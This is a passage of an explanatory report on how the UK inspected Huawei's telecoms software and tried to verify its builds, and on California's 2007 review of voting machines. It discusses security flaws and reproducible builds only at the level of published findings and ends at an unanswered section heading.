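Huawei bought extended support from the supplier, which could fix new flaws but could not change the underlying design. The Board and the operators called long-term reliance on the old system unacceptable. In 2019 Huawei agreed a plan with the operators to replace some circuit boards and move others to its own Linux-based operating system. The NCSC found Huawei's plans for maintaining the new system unsustainable too.

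By December 2019 Huawei and the operators had updated or replaced 17% of the affected circuit boards. The HCSEC Oversight Board's *Annual Report 2021* (2021) states that they dealt with another 35% during 2020 and that 23% reached the end of their supported life. They had therefore dealt with just over half of the boards in two years. The 23% no longer counted as work to be done, although the end of support did not fix them. The remaining 25% were still in use and in support.

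This was still real progress, given that the affected equipment was spread across the country and engineers often had to visit it in person during the pandemic. The HCSEC Oversight Board said a national-scale risk remained, but any new flaw in the old system would do considerably less damage than two years earlier. It expected the work planned for 2021 to reduce the risk to a manageable level.

### The broadband flaws of 2019

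In 2019 HCSEC found critical vulnerabilities in the code that processed messages from users in Huawei's fixed broadband equipment. The old operating system made the vulnerabilities worse because it lacked modern defences. The operators had to take what the HCSEC Oversight Board called "extraordinary action" to reduce the danger.

Huawei patched the vulnerabilities on time, but in doing so it added a command that turned off the product's additional layers of protection. An attacker who got past one defence could have used the command to disable the others. The Board took this as a sign of "a complete lack of security awareness".

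The NCSC judged the original code so poor that it told Huawei to rewrite it completely and redesign the product's security. Huawei updated a large amount of code in 2019 but did not complete the rewrite, and promised the redesign by June 2020. A year after that deadline, the HCSEC Oversight Board reported that Huawei had fixed all the vulnerabilities and rewritten some of the relevant code, which HCSEC had then re-examined. The board did not say whether Huawei had finished the redesign.

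### The $2 billion promise

In 2016 HCSEC reported that Huawei was not properly tracking its source code or the tools it used to build software. Huawei rejected the findings, but two years later HCSEC and the NCSC found the same problems across its product lines.

In September 2018 the HCSEC Oversight Board asked Huawei for a plan to repair one product, the 4G base station. The plan Huawei delivered in October acknowledged the problems but mostly described the company's existing processes and what they should achieve. The NCSC and the operators found it unacceptable. Huawei had another four weeks to improve it but, according to the Board, made no substantive progress.

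The NCSC wrote to Huawei again, and this time the company accepted the criticism and promised to spend $2 billion over five years on transforming how it developed software. The Board welcomed the money but called it a proposed budget for activities that Huawei had not yet specified. The NCSC's technical director thought five years was roughly the best anyone could expect.

A year later the NCSC had still not seen a credible plan or a reasonable allocation of the money. Huawei's new 5G products were only slightly better than its 4G ones, and the broadband equipment with the critical vulnerabilities had already been through the programme. The HCSEC Oversight Board acknowledged that the programme was only in its second year, but saw "no sign of genuine transformation".

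The Board had no formal power to supervise Huawei's company-wide transformation programme. Its report on 2020 lists the programme only among subjects it had discussed with Huawei in previous years. The programme was due to run until 2023, so the report cannot show whether it eventually worked, but the Board had seen no convincing results by the end of 2020.

Huawei was much better at fixing specific flaws than at improving its engineering overall. The HCSEC Oversight Board confirmed that during 2020 Huawei effectively repaired every vulnerability that HCSEC discovered and reported. But the Board found "no overall improvement" that year towards the quality of software engineering and security that the NCSC expected.

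Both findings can be true because HCSEC's reports gave Huawei a list of things to correct. An engineer can quickly fix an unsafe memory copy, but the next product will contain more of them if its programmers still work the same way. Measurements became less useful for a similar reason. Once HCSEC had reported the number of OpenSSL copies in a product, Huawei could reduce that number without managing its other components any better. In 2020, the HCSEC Oversight Board observed that improvements in the basic measures were still fixes for specific issues from earlier reports. It wanted to see sustained improvement across several versions of several products, because one good build would be little evidence that the next would also be good.

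### How the Board's verdict changed

In 2016 the HCSEC Oversight Board concluded that HCSEC had met its obligation to provide assurance that any risks to national security from Huawei's involvement in critical networks "have been sufficiently mitigated". It reported that Huawei's code had fewer basic errors and was measurably better than five years earlier, but was still below industry good practice. The Board reached the same overall conclusion in its 2017 report to the UK National Security Adviser.

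The evidence for those verdicts was weaker than they implied. Huawei's headquarters had been sending HCSEC only part of the source code, and HCSEC could not yet show that the code it read matched the software in use. The HCSEC Oversight Board later recalled that the 2017 report had described the assurance as limited for these reasons, but this had not changed the overall verdict.

In July 2018, the Board said that it could provide "only limited assurance" that the risks had been sufficiently mitigated, because no one had proven that the source code matched the binary and because some outside software was about to lose support. The Board repeated "limited assurance" in 2019 and 2020, and added that the risks of future products would be difficult to manage until Huawei corrected its underlying processes.

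"Limited assurance" described how well the country could manage the risks over the long term. The HCSEC Oversight Board stressed that it was not a judgement on the current security of British networks, and that they were no more vulnerable than a year earlier. Inspection had probably made them safer, because operators knew about more flaws and could protect against them. Even limited assurance was possible only because HCSEC had made the defects fairly well understood. The NCSC could use that knowledge to tell Huawei directly how to repair a product, as it did in one case in 2019, but it did not consider this sustainable.

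The NCSC saw the discoveries as a sign that the arrangement was working. That is fair as a judgment of detection, which was HCSEC's job. But the British strategy assumed that Huawei already followed good industry practice, and inspection could not make it do so. In 2021 the HCSEC Oversight Board expected the NCSC to be able to give better assurance in future, mainly because of a telecommunications security law then before Parliament.

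### Intent, and flaws nobody found

The NCSC said in both 2019 and 2020 that it did not believe the defects resulted from Chinese state interference. It blamed poor basic engineering and security practice, and said many different attackers could exploit the defects. The defects fit this explanation because they were numerous, spread across Huawei's products and sometimes detectable with ordinary tools, whereas a saboteur would want a few discreet flaws. Many also threatened the reliability of equipment Huawei was trying to sell.

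The NCSC's judgement covered only the defects that HCSEC had identified. It could not rule out a backdoor that HCSEC had missed, or a deliberate flaw among the hundreds of apparently accidental ones. The software on the base station's circuit board contained about 1,200 unsafe calls, and a planted one might have looked just like the rest. Poor code therefore makes carelessness the most likely explanation for any particular flaw, but it also makes a deliberate flaw harder to spot. As with the two Linux lines, evidence of intent would usually have to come from outside the code, for example from development records or intelligence.

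HCSEC's results suggest that an inspection can miss a lot. In 2015 the inspectors found subtler and more serious issues as their skills improved. In 2019 the number of reported vulnerabilities rose significantly. The NCSC attributed the rise to HCSEC's growing effectiveness and some especially poor components, not to a further decline in Huawei's work. Earlier, less capable inspections had probably missed some of those flaws for years. The NCSC also thought that products HCSEC had not yet examined were highly likely to contain new problems.

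## How did inspectors check that the code they read was the code in use?

For most of HCSEC's first decade, its inspectors couldn't confirm that the code they read was the code in use. HCSEC first tried to match Huawei's source code to the company's released software in 2011, had succeeded with one product by 2018, and reported eight verified builds for 2019.

Even a perfect review of source code can't show whether a network is secure if the network runs different software. Tom's Hardware's *UK Report* pointed out that Huawei could have given the inspectors a clean version and installed one with a backdoor in the network. An honest vendor can cause the same problem by losing track of which files went into which release.

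### Comparing two builds

Suppose a vendor releases a program whose file contains five numbers. The first is the minute it was built, which the compiler adds automatically, and the other four are instructions. An inspector builds the same source code one minute later, then calculates a fingerprint of both files by starting at zero and, for each number in turn, multiplying the running total by 31, adding the number and keeping the last four digits.

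| File | Contents | Fingerprint |
|---|---|---|
| Vendor's release, built at 10:05 | 5, 72, 18, 90, 41 | 2686 |
| Inspector's build, at 10:06 | 6, 72, 18, 90, 41 | 6207 |
| Altered program, built at 10:05 | 5, 72, 18, 91, 41 | 2717 |

The first two programs have identical instructions but very different fingerprints, because the one-minute difference affects every later step of the rule. The third program has an altered instruction, which could be a backdoor, yet its fingerprint is much closer to the vendor's. Inspectors can therefore tell from a mismatch that two files differ, but not whether the difference matters.

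To find out, the inspector has to compare the files number by number and trace each difference to its cause. Here only the first number differs. If the inspector sets the clock back to 10:05 and builds again, the fingerprint is 2686, which confirms that the clock caused the difference. Real hashes, such as SHA-256, are far longer, so nobody can feasibly make a different file with the same hash. They work on any file, including one that holds an AI model's weights.

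Real programs differ between builds for many similar reasons. In one week's work, Reproducible Builds (2017) listed programs whose output contained the date, the name of the build folder, or a random memory address. A vendor can prevent such differences, for example by fixing the date that the compiler records, so that the inspector only has to compare two hashes. The Oversight Board called such a build a "repeatable build".

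Huawei's build process was so complex that the HCSEC Oversight Board accepted binary equivalence as an interim step. Equivalence is easier for the vendor to achieve than an identical copy but harder for the inspector to check, because someone has to judge every remaining difference. The attempted Linux backdoor depended on one missing character, so even a small unexplained difference could matter.

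### The missing source code

HCSEC failed in its 2011 attempt because it didn't have all the code. The HCSEC Oversight Board later explained that a delivery team at Huawei's headquarters had been extracting only the source code for features that British operators had bought. Inspectors can't reliably rebuild a whole program from part of its source.

The Board's early reports contained little sign of the problem. The HCSEC Oversight Board's *HCSEC Report* said that HCSEC had developed tools for checking equivalence during 2014. A year later, the Board's *Huawei Cyber Security Evaluation* called equivalence a key capability for long-term assurance and said the initial work "shows promise". It also described a tool that picked out the code a product really used from a "massive oversubscription of code". HCSEC was apparently receiving a great deal of code it didn't need while lacking some that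 it did, so the size of a delivery didn't show whether it was complete.

In December 2016 Huawei promised to supply full code and build environments, and binary equivalence across all its products. The fuller packages it sent in 2017 confirmed that HCSEC's earlier source reviews had used incomplete material. Even in 2020, the HCSEC Oversight Board wrote only that full code "appears to have been provided" since 2017. The best test of completeness is a successful rebuild, because a missing file will usually stop the build or change the result. HCSEC could not yet rebuild most products.

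HCSEC's inspectors also tested working equipment and examined binaries directly, as they did when they counted unsafe memory functions in the 4G base station. The flaws they found that way were certainly in the software they tested. The lack of a confirmed match between source code and binaries mattered most when a source review found nothing wrong, because the code reviewed might not have been the code in use.

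### Four pilot products

Complete source code was not enough to check that it was the code in use, because Huawei could not reliably build the same binary from it twice. HCSEC had been doing most of the laborious work of matching builds, but it handed much of this to Huawei's developers and concentrated on verifying their results. The developers' investigation confirmed that the build process was not repeatable. The NCSC and HCSEC then asked Huawei to analyse four products from different parts of the company, and the HCSEC Oversight Board reported that all four had the same underlying problems.

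After considerable effort by both sides, one of the four products had a repeatable build. In its 2018 report, the HCSEC Oversight Board expected British operators to deploy this version and the other three products to follow in the first half of 2018. HCSEC, the NCSC and the operators had already chosen a second batch, and the Board expected to cover every remaining product by mid-2020. The Board described a much less encouraging position at the end of 2018.

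| Pilot product | Position at the end of 2018 |
|---|---|
| Broadband head end, which connects customers' lines to the network | Repeatable build achieved, but no British operator could deploy it |
| 4G base station | HCSEC had not finished checking Huawei's build |
| 4G core network | HCSEC was just beginning its checks |
| Optical transmission equipment | HCSEC had postponed its checks until 2019 |

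Operators could not deploy the successful version because it depended on things their networks did not have. Eight years after it opened, HCSEC had not verified a repeatable build of any version that a British operator was running.

### Why the builds would not repeat

The NCSC and the Board asked HCSEC to investigate the causes. The HCSEC Oversight Board published its findings, which fell into three areas:

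- **Build machines.** Huawei built its software on virtual machines, which are simulated computers that should start each build in a known, clean state. Many already contained source code, sometimes irrelevant, and leftovers from previous builds. If a build picks up an old file by mistake, its result depends on what the machine did before.
- **Tools.** Huawei's build environments contained several copies of the same tools, and tools that the build did not need. Many were long out of support. Some compilers could produce different results from the same source code, or changed how they optimised a program according to settings on the machine.
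- **Version control.** Huawei managed its product code, platform code and outside components in different ways. Components with the same version number sometimes differed significantly, and some new product releases contained older versions of components than the releases they replaced. Some components also depended on each other in a circle, which makes it hard to establish what to build first.

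These failures showed problems with Huawei's engineering, whatever they implied about its honesty. A company that cannot rebuild its own product does not know exactly what it has shipped, and its engineers may struggle to find the cause of a fault that a customer reports. The NCSC had demanded proper version control since 2010, and it now had limited confidence that Huawei understood what any given build contained.

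Huawei's own developers could not repeat the builds either, because of disorganized build machines and old compilers, so the failures do not suggest that the company was hiding a second version of its software. But a deliberate substitution would have been much harder to detect among so many innocent differences.

HCSEC and the NCSC decided that redesigning Huawei's build process from scratch would be better than continuing to match products one at a time. They doubted that the equivalence programme was worth continuing until Huawei had finished the redesign.

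In its reply to the 2019 report, Huawei made two claims that the report did not support. It said that the Board had attested that Huawei's equipment had no backdoors, and that opening its source code to review made its security assurance "verifiable". The NCSC had said only that Chinese state interference was not the likely cause of the defects already found. It had also said that it could not be confident that HCSEC was reading the source code of the software in use.

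### Eight builds or sixteen?

The work resumed on a larger scale in 2019. Huawei simplified and significantly improved the build process for certain products, and HCSEC wrote five reports on equivalence. The HCSEC Oversight Board said that HCSEC had verified eight product builds, which gave the Board confidence that HCSEC had inspected the specific products deployed in British networks. HCSEC had verified only one build the year before, but eight was still far fewer than the number of product evaluations it completed in 2019.

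The HCSEC Oversight Board gave the same figure in the next year's report, which stated that "during 2020" Huawei had provided products that met the NCSC's requirement for eight product builds. The published evidence establishes at least eight verified builds, but not sixteen. The two reports cover different calendar years, so read literally they describe two separate sets of eight. However, neither report names the builds, and the later one doesn't mention the earlier eight or give a running total, so the Board may have been reporting the same achievement again under a new date.

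Huawei also promised equivalence for officially released versions of all carrier products (equipment for telecoms operators) sold into the UK from December 2020. The reports don't make clear whether it kept this promise. The HCSEC Oversight Board repeated the promise in June 2021 but didn't say whether Huawei was meeting it. The promise appears to cover only new sales, so operators might have gone on running older versions that nobody had matched to source code.

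The NCSC doubted the progress would last, because in 2019 each match was still "a bespoke project", as the HCSEC Oversight Board put it. The NCSC wanted Huawei's normal build process to produce equivalent binaries automatically. Otherwise, the inspectors would have to start again with every release, and Huawei would have to keep paying for special work that only its British customers had requested.

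### What a match leaves open

A match confirms where a binary came from, but the HCSEC Oversight Board stressed that it provides no assurance about engineering quality or security. If the source code contains an unsafe memory copy, a repeatable build will reproduce it.

A match also applies only until the next patch, and the NCSC wanted HCSEC to repeat the check for every deployed version it had assessed. Someone must then confirm that the equipment is running the verified file, because an operator may have installed a different one.

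The comparison does not cover hardware, and a chip with a hidden function could undermine software that matched its source code exactly. This concern became more pressing after the American sanctions, when Huawei began replacing American components with parts designed by other companies. HCSEC started to examine the modified products in late 2019. The HCSEC Oversight Board expected that being equally confident in them would take more effort and skill in analysing hardware, which might limit how many products operators could use.

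The most difficult gap concerns the compiler, which is itself a program that someone has to build. Ken Thompson, one of the creators of the Unix operating system, explained the danger in his 1984 lecture *Reflections on Trusting Trust*. His attack works as follows:

1. An attacker changes the compiler's source code so that, whenever it compiles the Unix login program, it adds a secret password. The source code of the login program remains clean.
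2. The attacker adds another change, so that whenever the compiler compiles a new copy of itself, it inserts both changes into the copy.
3. The attacker builds this corrupted compiler, installs the binary and restores the compiler's original source code.

The attack no longer appears in any source code. But anyone who uses the installed compiler to build a new one from the clean source will get another corrupted compiler, which will also add the secret password to the login program.

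Thompson's argument applies to binary equivalence. HCSEC needed Huawei's build environments, including the compilers, to reproduce Huawei's software. If one of those compilers had been corrupt, HCSEC's build and Huawei's release would have contained the same backdoor and still matched. The Board reported that Huawei's compilers were outdated and inconsistent, not that they were corrupt, but a match alone could not have ruled out corruption.

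The computer scientist David A. Wheeler later developed a way to test for such an attack. An inspector compiles the suspect compiler's source code with a second, unrelated compiler, then uses the result to compile the same source code again. If the suspect compiler was built from that source without tampering, the final binary should be identical to the suspect compiler's binary. The attack can escape detection only if the second compiler contains matching malicious code. But the test requires compilers that always produce the same output from the same input, and some of Huawei's compilers did not.

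### Reproducible builds in open-source software

Linking source code to binaries seems to be less common than the NCSC suggested in 2019, when it called this "usual with a well-managed software engineering process". Open-source projects have worked on the problem for years, yet Debian, a widely used operating system based on Linux, made reproducibility a condition of entry to its next release only in May 2026.

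Debian's *bits from the release team* (2026) announced that Debian "must ship reproducible packages" (a package is a piece of software prepared for installation). Debian's systems now block new packages that fail the reproducibility test from entering "testing", the collection that will become the next stable release. They also block updates that make a previously reproducible package fail. The release team said it would allow exceptions but hoped there would be fewer over time.

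When Debian builds a package, it creates a file that records details of the build. A separate service uses this file to try to rebuild the package bit for bit. Linuxiac's *Debian Now Blocks Non-Reproducible Packages from Testing* reported that the service had reproduced 23,728 packages, more than 98% of those for the next release. The service checks the packages that Debian distributes, according to the title of a May 2026 talk listed by Reproducible Builds (2026). HCSEC needed the same kind of check for the software in British networks.

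Debian's standard is stricter than HCSEC's, because the rebuilt package must be identical. Anyone can also repeat the test, since the source code is public, whereas only HCSEC's vetted staff could check Huawei's builds for the British government. But Debian's task is easier in one respect, because it can test thousands of mostly separate packages one at a time, while a base station combines a lot of interdependent code in a single product.

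Some outsiders thought that the British were holding Huawei to an unusual standard. The American programmer John Gilmore (2020), in *UK "HCSEC" UK-cleared engineers try to prove Huawei gear secure*, described the security problems that HCSEC was finding as typical of the whole industry. Debian's experience partly supports him, because fully reproducible software was far from universal in 2019. But contaminated build machines, or different components with the same version number, would be serious faults even if nobody had asked for a repeatable build.

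Debian can also keep a package out of its next release until someone fixes the build, a means of enforcement that the British arrangement lacked.

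## What did California's 2007 voting machine review find and change?

California's Secretary of State could bar faulty voting systems from elections, and Debra Bowen used that power in 2007. University researchers had found that an attacker could defeat the built-in security of all three systems they examined. On 3 August Bowen withdrew her approval of all three, then approved them again the same night under strict conditions. The conditions mostly changed how counties used the machines. There is much less evidence that the makers rewrote their software, and one of the versions the researchers examined kept its approval until 2019.

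### Which vendors took part

Under state law, Bowen could withdraw approval from any voting system that proved "defective, obsolete or otherwise unacceptable". Eight certified systems were in use when she announced the review in March 2007, according to Government Technology's *California Decertifies Voting Machines, Conditions Applied for Use*. Diebold, Hart InterCivic and Sequoia each submitted one for review. Vendors held back four others because they did not intend any county to use them after 1 January 2008.

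The eighth was InkaVote Plus, a product of Election Systems and Software (ES&S) that only Los Angeles County used. The California Secretary of State's *Conditional Approval of Election Systems and Software Inka Vote Plus* records that on 26 March Bowen gave ES&S thirty days to deliver a working system, its source code and payment for the review. She then set a final deadline of 11 May and repeated her demands twice in June. ES&S agreed to take part on 25 June and delivered the last items a day later, which left too little time to test the system. Bowen withdrew her approval on 3 August because the company had prevented her from reviewing the system and had broken the conditions of its 2006 approval. Her order does not explain the delay.

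Before Bowen announced that decision, the security expert Bruce Schneier had predicted that other vendors would copy ES&S. He argued in *More on the California Voting Machine Review* that refusing to co-operate had carried no penalty, so a company could avoid embarrassment by holding back its worst code until the reviewers ran out of time. Bowen's order did penalize ES&S, but fairly mildly, since it applied only from the presidential primary of February 2008 and ES&S won a new, conditional approval in January.

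The primary also made the schedule tight. Withdrawing approval could affect only elections at least six months away, and California had moved its primary from June to 5 February. Bowen therefore had to decide by the end of 3 August, and she announced her decision at 11:45 that night, according to ABC News' *E-Voting OK With New Security*.

### How the teams worked

Matt Bishop, a computer scientist at the University of California, Davis, led the red teams and the accessibility team, which checked whether disabled voters and speakers of other languages could use the machines. David Wagner of the University of California, Berkeley, led the teams that read source code and documents. The review involved 42 researchers, according to *California voting systems code review now released* by Blaze (2007), who led the Sequoia code team. They worked from 31 May to 20 July, whereas HCSEC had permanent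 staff who could return to a product.

The Sequoia source code reached Berkeley a week after the review began. The reviewers there had no voting machines, because the state kept the equipment in Sacramento for the red teams, so they worked closely with the Sequoia red team. This helped both groups, because someone reading code may suspect that a flaw is exploitable without being able to prove it, and an attacker without the code may take days to find the same flaw. The red team later described its work in *An Experience in Testing the Security of Real-world Electronic Voting Systems*, where Balzarotti, Banks and colleagues wrote that having both the code and the machines let them carry out attacks that had previously been only theoretical.

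Blaze and colleagues tested the hypothesis that the voting system was secure from tampering. Once they had strong evidence against it in one part of the system, they moved on to another. They reasoned that it makes little difference whether an attacker has three methods or thirty if all have the same effect. This approach suited a seven-week review and gave Bowen a clear answer, but it did not give Sequoia a complete list of what to repair. The team warned that its findings might be only the "tip of the iceberg".

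In some cases, late and missing documents hindered the reviewers more than the schedule did. The lawyer Candice Hoke led the team that examined Diebold's documents. Hoke and Kettyle (2007), in *Documentation Assessment of the Diebold Voting System*, recounted that they received a disc labelled as Diebold's technical package that contained none of the proper technical documents. Two of the missing packages arrived on 13 July, the day their evaluation was due to end. The team spent the last week, reserved for writing, on almost 1,000 pages of new material, and never obtained a full set. Bishop complained that documents arriving that day were too late to help the red teams.

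Hoke and Kettyle also compared the Diebold system in Sacramento with the configuration that California had certified. They found numerous differences, including an uncertified component and largely disabled security settings. The Sequoia reviewers did not try to check that their source code matched the binary in use, and they lacked the full build environment needed to do so. California therefore did not address the problem that occupied HCSEC for most of a decade. A mismatch would not have invalidated the red teams' findings, because they broke into working machines.

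### What the reviewers found

Each system had electronic voting machines, scanners that read paper ballots, and software on county computers that prepared the ballots and added up the results. Memory cards, cartridges or cables carried data between the polling places and the county office. The makers had mostly designed each part to accept data from the others without checking it, so a person who corrupted one machine might be able to corrupt the rest.

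Wagner warned in a talk later that year, *Report on the California top-to-bottom review*, that one person with no special access could introduce a malicious program that would infect every machine in a county. The table draws on his talk and the source code reports.

| System | Example of a weak protection | How tampering could spread |
|---|---|---|
| Diebold | One password was "diebold" | From a memory card to the county's computers, then on new cards to other machines |
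| Hart | Polling-place machines accepted new software from a county computer without checking its identity | From one machine to the county computer, then to every machine connected to it |
| Sequoia | The secret keys were apparently the same in all its equipment, inside and outside California | From corrupted software on one machine to others, under some configurations |

Inguva, Rescorla and colleagues tested some parts of the Hart attack but did not have time to try it from beginning to end (*Source Code Review of the Hart InterCivic Voting System*, 2007). Balzarotti and colleagues built and ran complete attacks of this kind against real, certified equipment, and said the work needed only ordinary skill.

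Ballot secrecy was also at risk. Diebold's touchscreen stored votes in the order people cast them and stamped each with the time. Anyone who could read those records and had noted the order of voters could work out how each person voted. Inguva and colleagues found that election staff with access to Hart's raw records could do much the same.

The Diebold source code team concluded that the software's controls "do not provide sufficient security to guarantee a trustworthy election" (quoted in Rubin, 2007, *California source code study results*). The Sequoia team found no case in which cryptography was used correctly and achieved its apparent purpose. Sequoia had invented its own way of encrypting passwords, which only added a few fixed letters to the end of each one.

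Blaze was struck by the "utter banality" of most of the flaws. The makers of all three systems had made elementary errors, often the same ones. Balzarotti and colleagues found code that checked the size of incoming data against itself instead of against the space available. HCSEC found the same mistake in Huawei's base station more than a decade later. The errors looked careless, as Huawei's did. Blaze thought a well-disguised backdoor would have been almost impossible to detect, but that nobody would have needed one because the software already had so many ways in.

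Schneier (2007), in *Assurance*, took the quick discovery of major flaws as a sign that the makers had designed the machines badly, not that the review was thorough. A review that short might have missed serious flaws in a better product.

### Why federal laboratories had passed these systems

After Florida's disputed presidential count in 2000, Congress passed the Help America Vote Act of 2002, which offered states $3.86 billion for new voting technology and other improvements. Balzarotti and colleagues think the money led some counties to buy, and some vendors to sell, products that were not ready. Before California's review, private laboratories known as Independent Testing Authorities had tested all of this equipment against voluntary federal standards. The vendors paid for the tests, and the laboratories did not publish the results.

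The Wyle laboratory examined the hardware and built-in software of the Diebold and Hart systems, and the CIBER laboratory examined the rest of the software and the documents. Hoke and Kettyle thought Wyle's reports on Diebold were reasonably thorough. CIBER's 16-page report contained too little about its methods, tests or results for a reader to judge whether Diebold had met the standards.

*Documentation Review of the Hart InterCivic System 6.2.1 Voting System* (Hall and Quilter, 2007) found that the laboratories had not tested some relevant requirements, and that splitting the work between two companies had caused serious gaps. An earlier study, *Security Analysis of the Diebold AccuBasic Interpreter* (Wagner, Jefferson and Bishop, 2006), examined programs that ran from the memory cards of Diebold machines, partly because the laboratories had not thoroughly reviewed them with the rest of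 the code.

Better coverage would not have been enough, because the standards set the wrong requirements. Balzarotti and colleagues explained that laboratories mostly checked whether a system worked and was usable, and did no substantial security testing. For instance, a rule might require programmers to check the size of incoming data, and a laboratory could confirm that the check existed without noticing that it was wrong. A mistake of this kind caused one of the exploitable flaws the team found.

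Counties also tested their machines before each election, but the systems had a special test mode. Malicious software could behave correctly in that mode and misbehave on election day, so Balzarotti and colleagues judged the tests useless for security.

Payment by the vendor may have contributed to the voting laboratories' leniency, but Huawei also paid for HCSEC, whose inspectors reported hundreds of flaws. HCSEC's inspectors looked for ways to attack the product, and government experts who could judge the work read their reports. The voting laboratories worked from a checklist, and hardly anyone outside could see what they had done.

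State officials were in a poor position to catch the failures. Hall and Quilter credited California's own consultants with documenting serious problems that the federal process had missed. But they also described a "leaky pipeline", in which a problem found at one stage of approval might go unaddressed at later ones. They doubted that the state could have made an informed decision from the documents available to them. Bowen called counties and voters "the victims of a federal certification process" that had not done its job.

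### What the reviewers could publish

The vendors' code was a trade secret, and precise instructions for exploiting it would have helped anyone who wanted to tamper with an election. The Berkeley reviewers worked in a small, windowless room with an alarm, a safe and a lock that the building's master key did not open. They kept their computers off the internet and kept even the cleaners out. When they delivered their report on 20 July, they destroyed all the proprietary material they had received.

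Officials in Sacramento kept the machines, documents and code in locked cages under video surveillance. Campus Technology's *California Enlists Higher Ed Hackers To Test Voting Machines* (2007) reported that the public could watch the red team work via monitors in the Secretary of State's building.

The teams had instructions to split their reports into a public part, which described the flaws and their consequences, and a private appendix. The appendix held the details most useful to an attacker and went only to Bowen and the vendor concerned, according to *Where are the California E-Voting Reports?* (2007), a post on the technology policy blog Freedom to Tinker. In the Sequoia report, Blaze and colleagues replaced file names, function names and line numbers with numbered markers, and listed what the markers stood for in a separate annex. Along with the source code reports, the California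 Secretary of State published a statement by Wagner on protecting security-sensitive information. In his later talk, Wagner also disguised the letters that Sequoia's software added to passwords.

The split worked well because outsiders could see what kind of mistakes the vendors had made and how much they mattered, while the vendors could find the exact lines to repair. The three source code reports came to more than 300 pages, and Blaze believed they were the most detailed public account of how such systems worked.

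The staggered release of the reports worked less well. Bowen released the red team reports first and held a public hearing on 30 July, while her office was still checking the source code and document reports for sensitive details. Freedom to Tinker objected that the researchers had already removed such details and understood them better than the office's lawyers did. It also suggested that Bowen feared the political effect of even worse findings, but offered no direct evidence. The source code reports appeared on 2 August. By then, critics had used the hearing to attack the review for ignoring matters that the unpublished reports almost certainly covered.

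### The objection that the tests were unrealistic

*E-voting machine vendors, election officials slam review* (Harmon, 2007) reported that vendors and election officials told the hearing Bowen had failed to consider how people would respond to a real attack. One vendor's spokeswoman complained to IT World Canada that the tests had not followed real election procedures. The argument was that staff at a real polling place would guard the machines, check the seals and notice anyone interfering with them.

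The red teams had left all this out on purpose. *Overview of Red Team Reports* (Bishop, 2007) describes their task as attacking the systems without assuming any safeguards that vendors, the state or counties might have added. This separates the product's own security from the diligence of the people using it, but the results therefore don't show how likely a successful attack would have been in a particular county.

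Blaze replied that the red teams had not won by cheating, because the source code showed that the protections they faced "simply don't work properly". This means that laboratory conditions did not create the flaws, but it doesn't show how well a county could guard a weak machine. Blaze and colleagues acknowledged in their report that the practical danger depended heavily on local controls, which they had not examined. But they pointed out that Sequoia seemed to have designed its locks, seals and procedures as if the software were much more secure than it was.

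Procedures can also fail, by accident or because an insider ignores them. One vendor responded to a security finding by insisting that the problem could not occur because it would violate the procedures. Balzarotti and colleagues thought the vendor misunderstood what an attacker does. A test of InkaVote Plus that autumn supported this view, as another red team removed the seals with household materials and put them back without leaving a trace.

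Local officials had a better case when they complained about being left out. The California State Association of Counties (2007) supported the idea of a review but protested that Bowen had ignored repeated requests to include county election officials. Hoke and Kettyle listed the same omission among the major limitations of their study. They could not discuss the machines with local officials, watch staff use them in an election or read the questions that counties had sent to the vendors. Election staff could have told the reviewers which written safeguards were not followed in practice, although they could not have repaired the cryptography.

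### What Bowen ordered

Bowen withdrew approval from the three systems and reissued it with new conditions, partly so that counties could find all the rules for a system in one document. Government Technology listed the main ones:

- Counties could use Diebold and Sequoia touchscreens only for early voting and, on election day, one per polling place for disabled voters. They had to count every vote from these machines by hand.
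- Counties had to reinstall the software on every part of the system, block connections they did not need and keep a record of who had handled the equipment.
- Nobody could connect the equipment to a modem or a wireless network for any purpose.
- Close contests would require additional counting by hand.

California could impose these conditions because voters could use paper ballots instead of the machines. Bowen estimated that at least two-thirds of the 8.9 million people who voted in November 2006 had used paper ballots, so most voters would hardly notice the change. Lake County News reported that 37 of the state's 58 counties already had only one voting machine at each polling place. Without paper ballots, California's legal power would have been harder to use. The British government had no comparable substitute for the equipment in BT's network.

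After moving voters to paper, the state still relied on the vendors' software. Scanners from the same three companies read the ballots, and county computers added up the totals. But with paper, officials could check those totals against ballots that voters had marked themselves. Inguva and colleagues thought that examining the paper records would protect against some, but not all, of their attacks on Hart's system.

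Bowen did not limit the number of Hart's electronic voting machines, because her office considered the Hart system less vulnerable to some kinds of attack than the other two. The comparison may have been fair, but it was lenient toward Hart, because Inguva and colleagues had warned that a malicious voter might take over one or more of its machines and a poll worker might take over every machine in a precinct.

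The extra counts in close contests did not last. San Diego County challenged them, and in 2008 a state appeals court ruled that Bowen should have followed California's formal procedure for making regulations. She reissued the rules as emergency regulations, which are temporary, and the California Secretary of State's website now marks them "expired". State law still required counties to check a random 1% by hand after each election.

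### The separate ES&S review and Ohio's study

By the time Bowen received the InkaVote Plus system, the university teams were no longer available. She hired a consulting firm, Freeman, Craft & McGregor Group, which engaged the security company atsec to read the code and attack the machines. Their findings resembled those of the summer review. ES&S had used a very weak cipher that it or its supplier had designed, and a checksum that could detect accidental damage but not deliberate tampering. The red team altered an election file so that the machine no longer warned people who had voted for too many candidates.

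The accessibility experts found a fault that did not need an attacker. If a voter using the audio system chose a listed candidate and then tried to write in another name, the machine appeared to accept the new name but printed a ballot still marked for the first candidate, with the title of the office and no name in the write-in space.

California Secretary of State Bowen reapproved InkaVote Plus only for the way Los Angeles used it, which was to print ballots and warn voters of mistakes, not to record or count official votes. In December 2007 she also imposed conditions on other ES&S equipment, after evidence that its scanners could lose votes if staff did not calibrate them precisely or voters used light ink.

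Ohio's Secretary of State, Jennifer Brunner, sponsored a similar study, EVEREST (Evaluation and Validation of Election-Related Equipment, Standards and Testing), published in December 2007. Several of the California researchers took part. Balzarotti and colleagues examined ES&S equipment, and other teams studied products from Hart and from Premier, the new name for Diebold's voting business. The researchers again had both source code and machines, and Balzarotti and colleagues again built attacks that spread from one part of the system to another. The study led to a recommendation that Ohio decertify the systems.

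Ohio's EVEREST study provides a check on California's result. Ohio chose its own equipment and ran its own study, and the researchers still found cryptography that did not work and components that accepted any data they received without checking it. The two studies shared some staff, so they were not fully independent. Even so, four manufacturers had obtained approval for products with similar basic faults, which suggests that the approval system failed as well as the companies.

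### Did the vendors fix the flaws?

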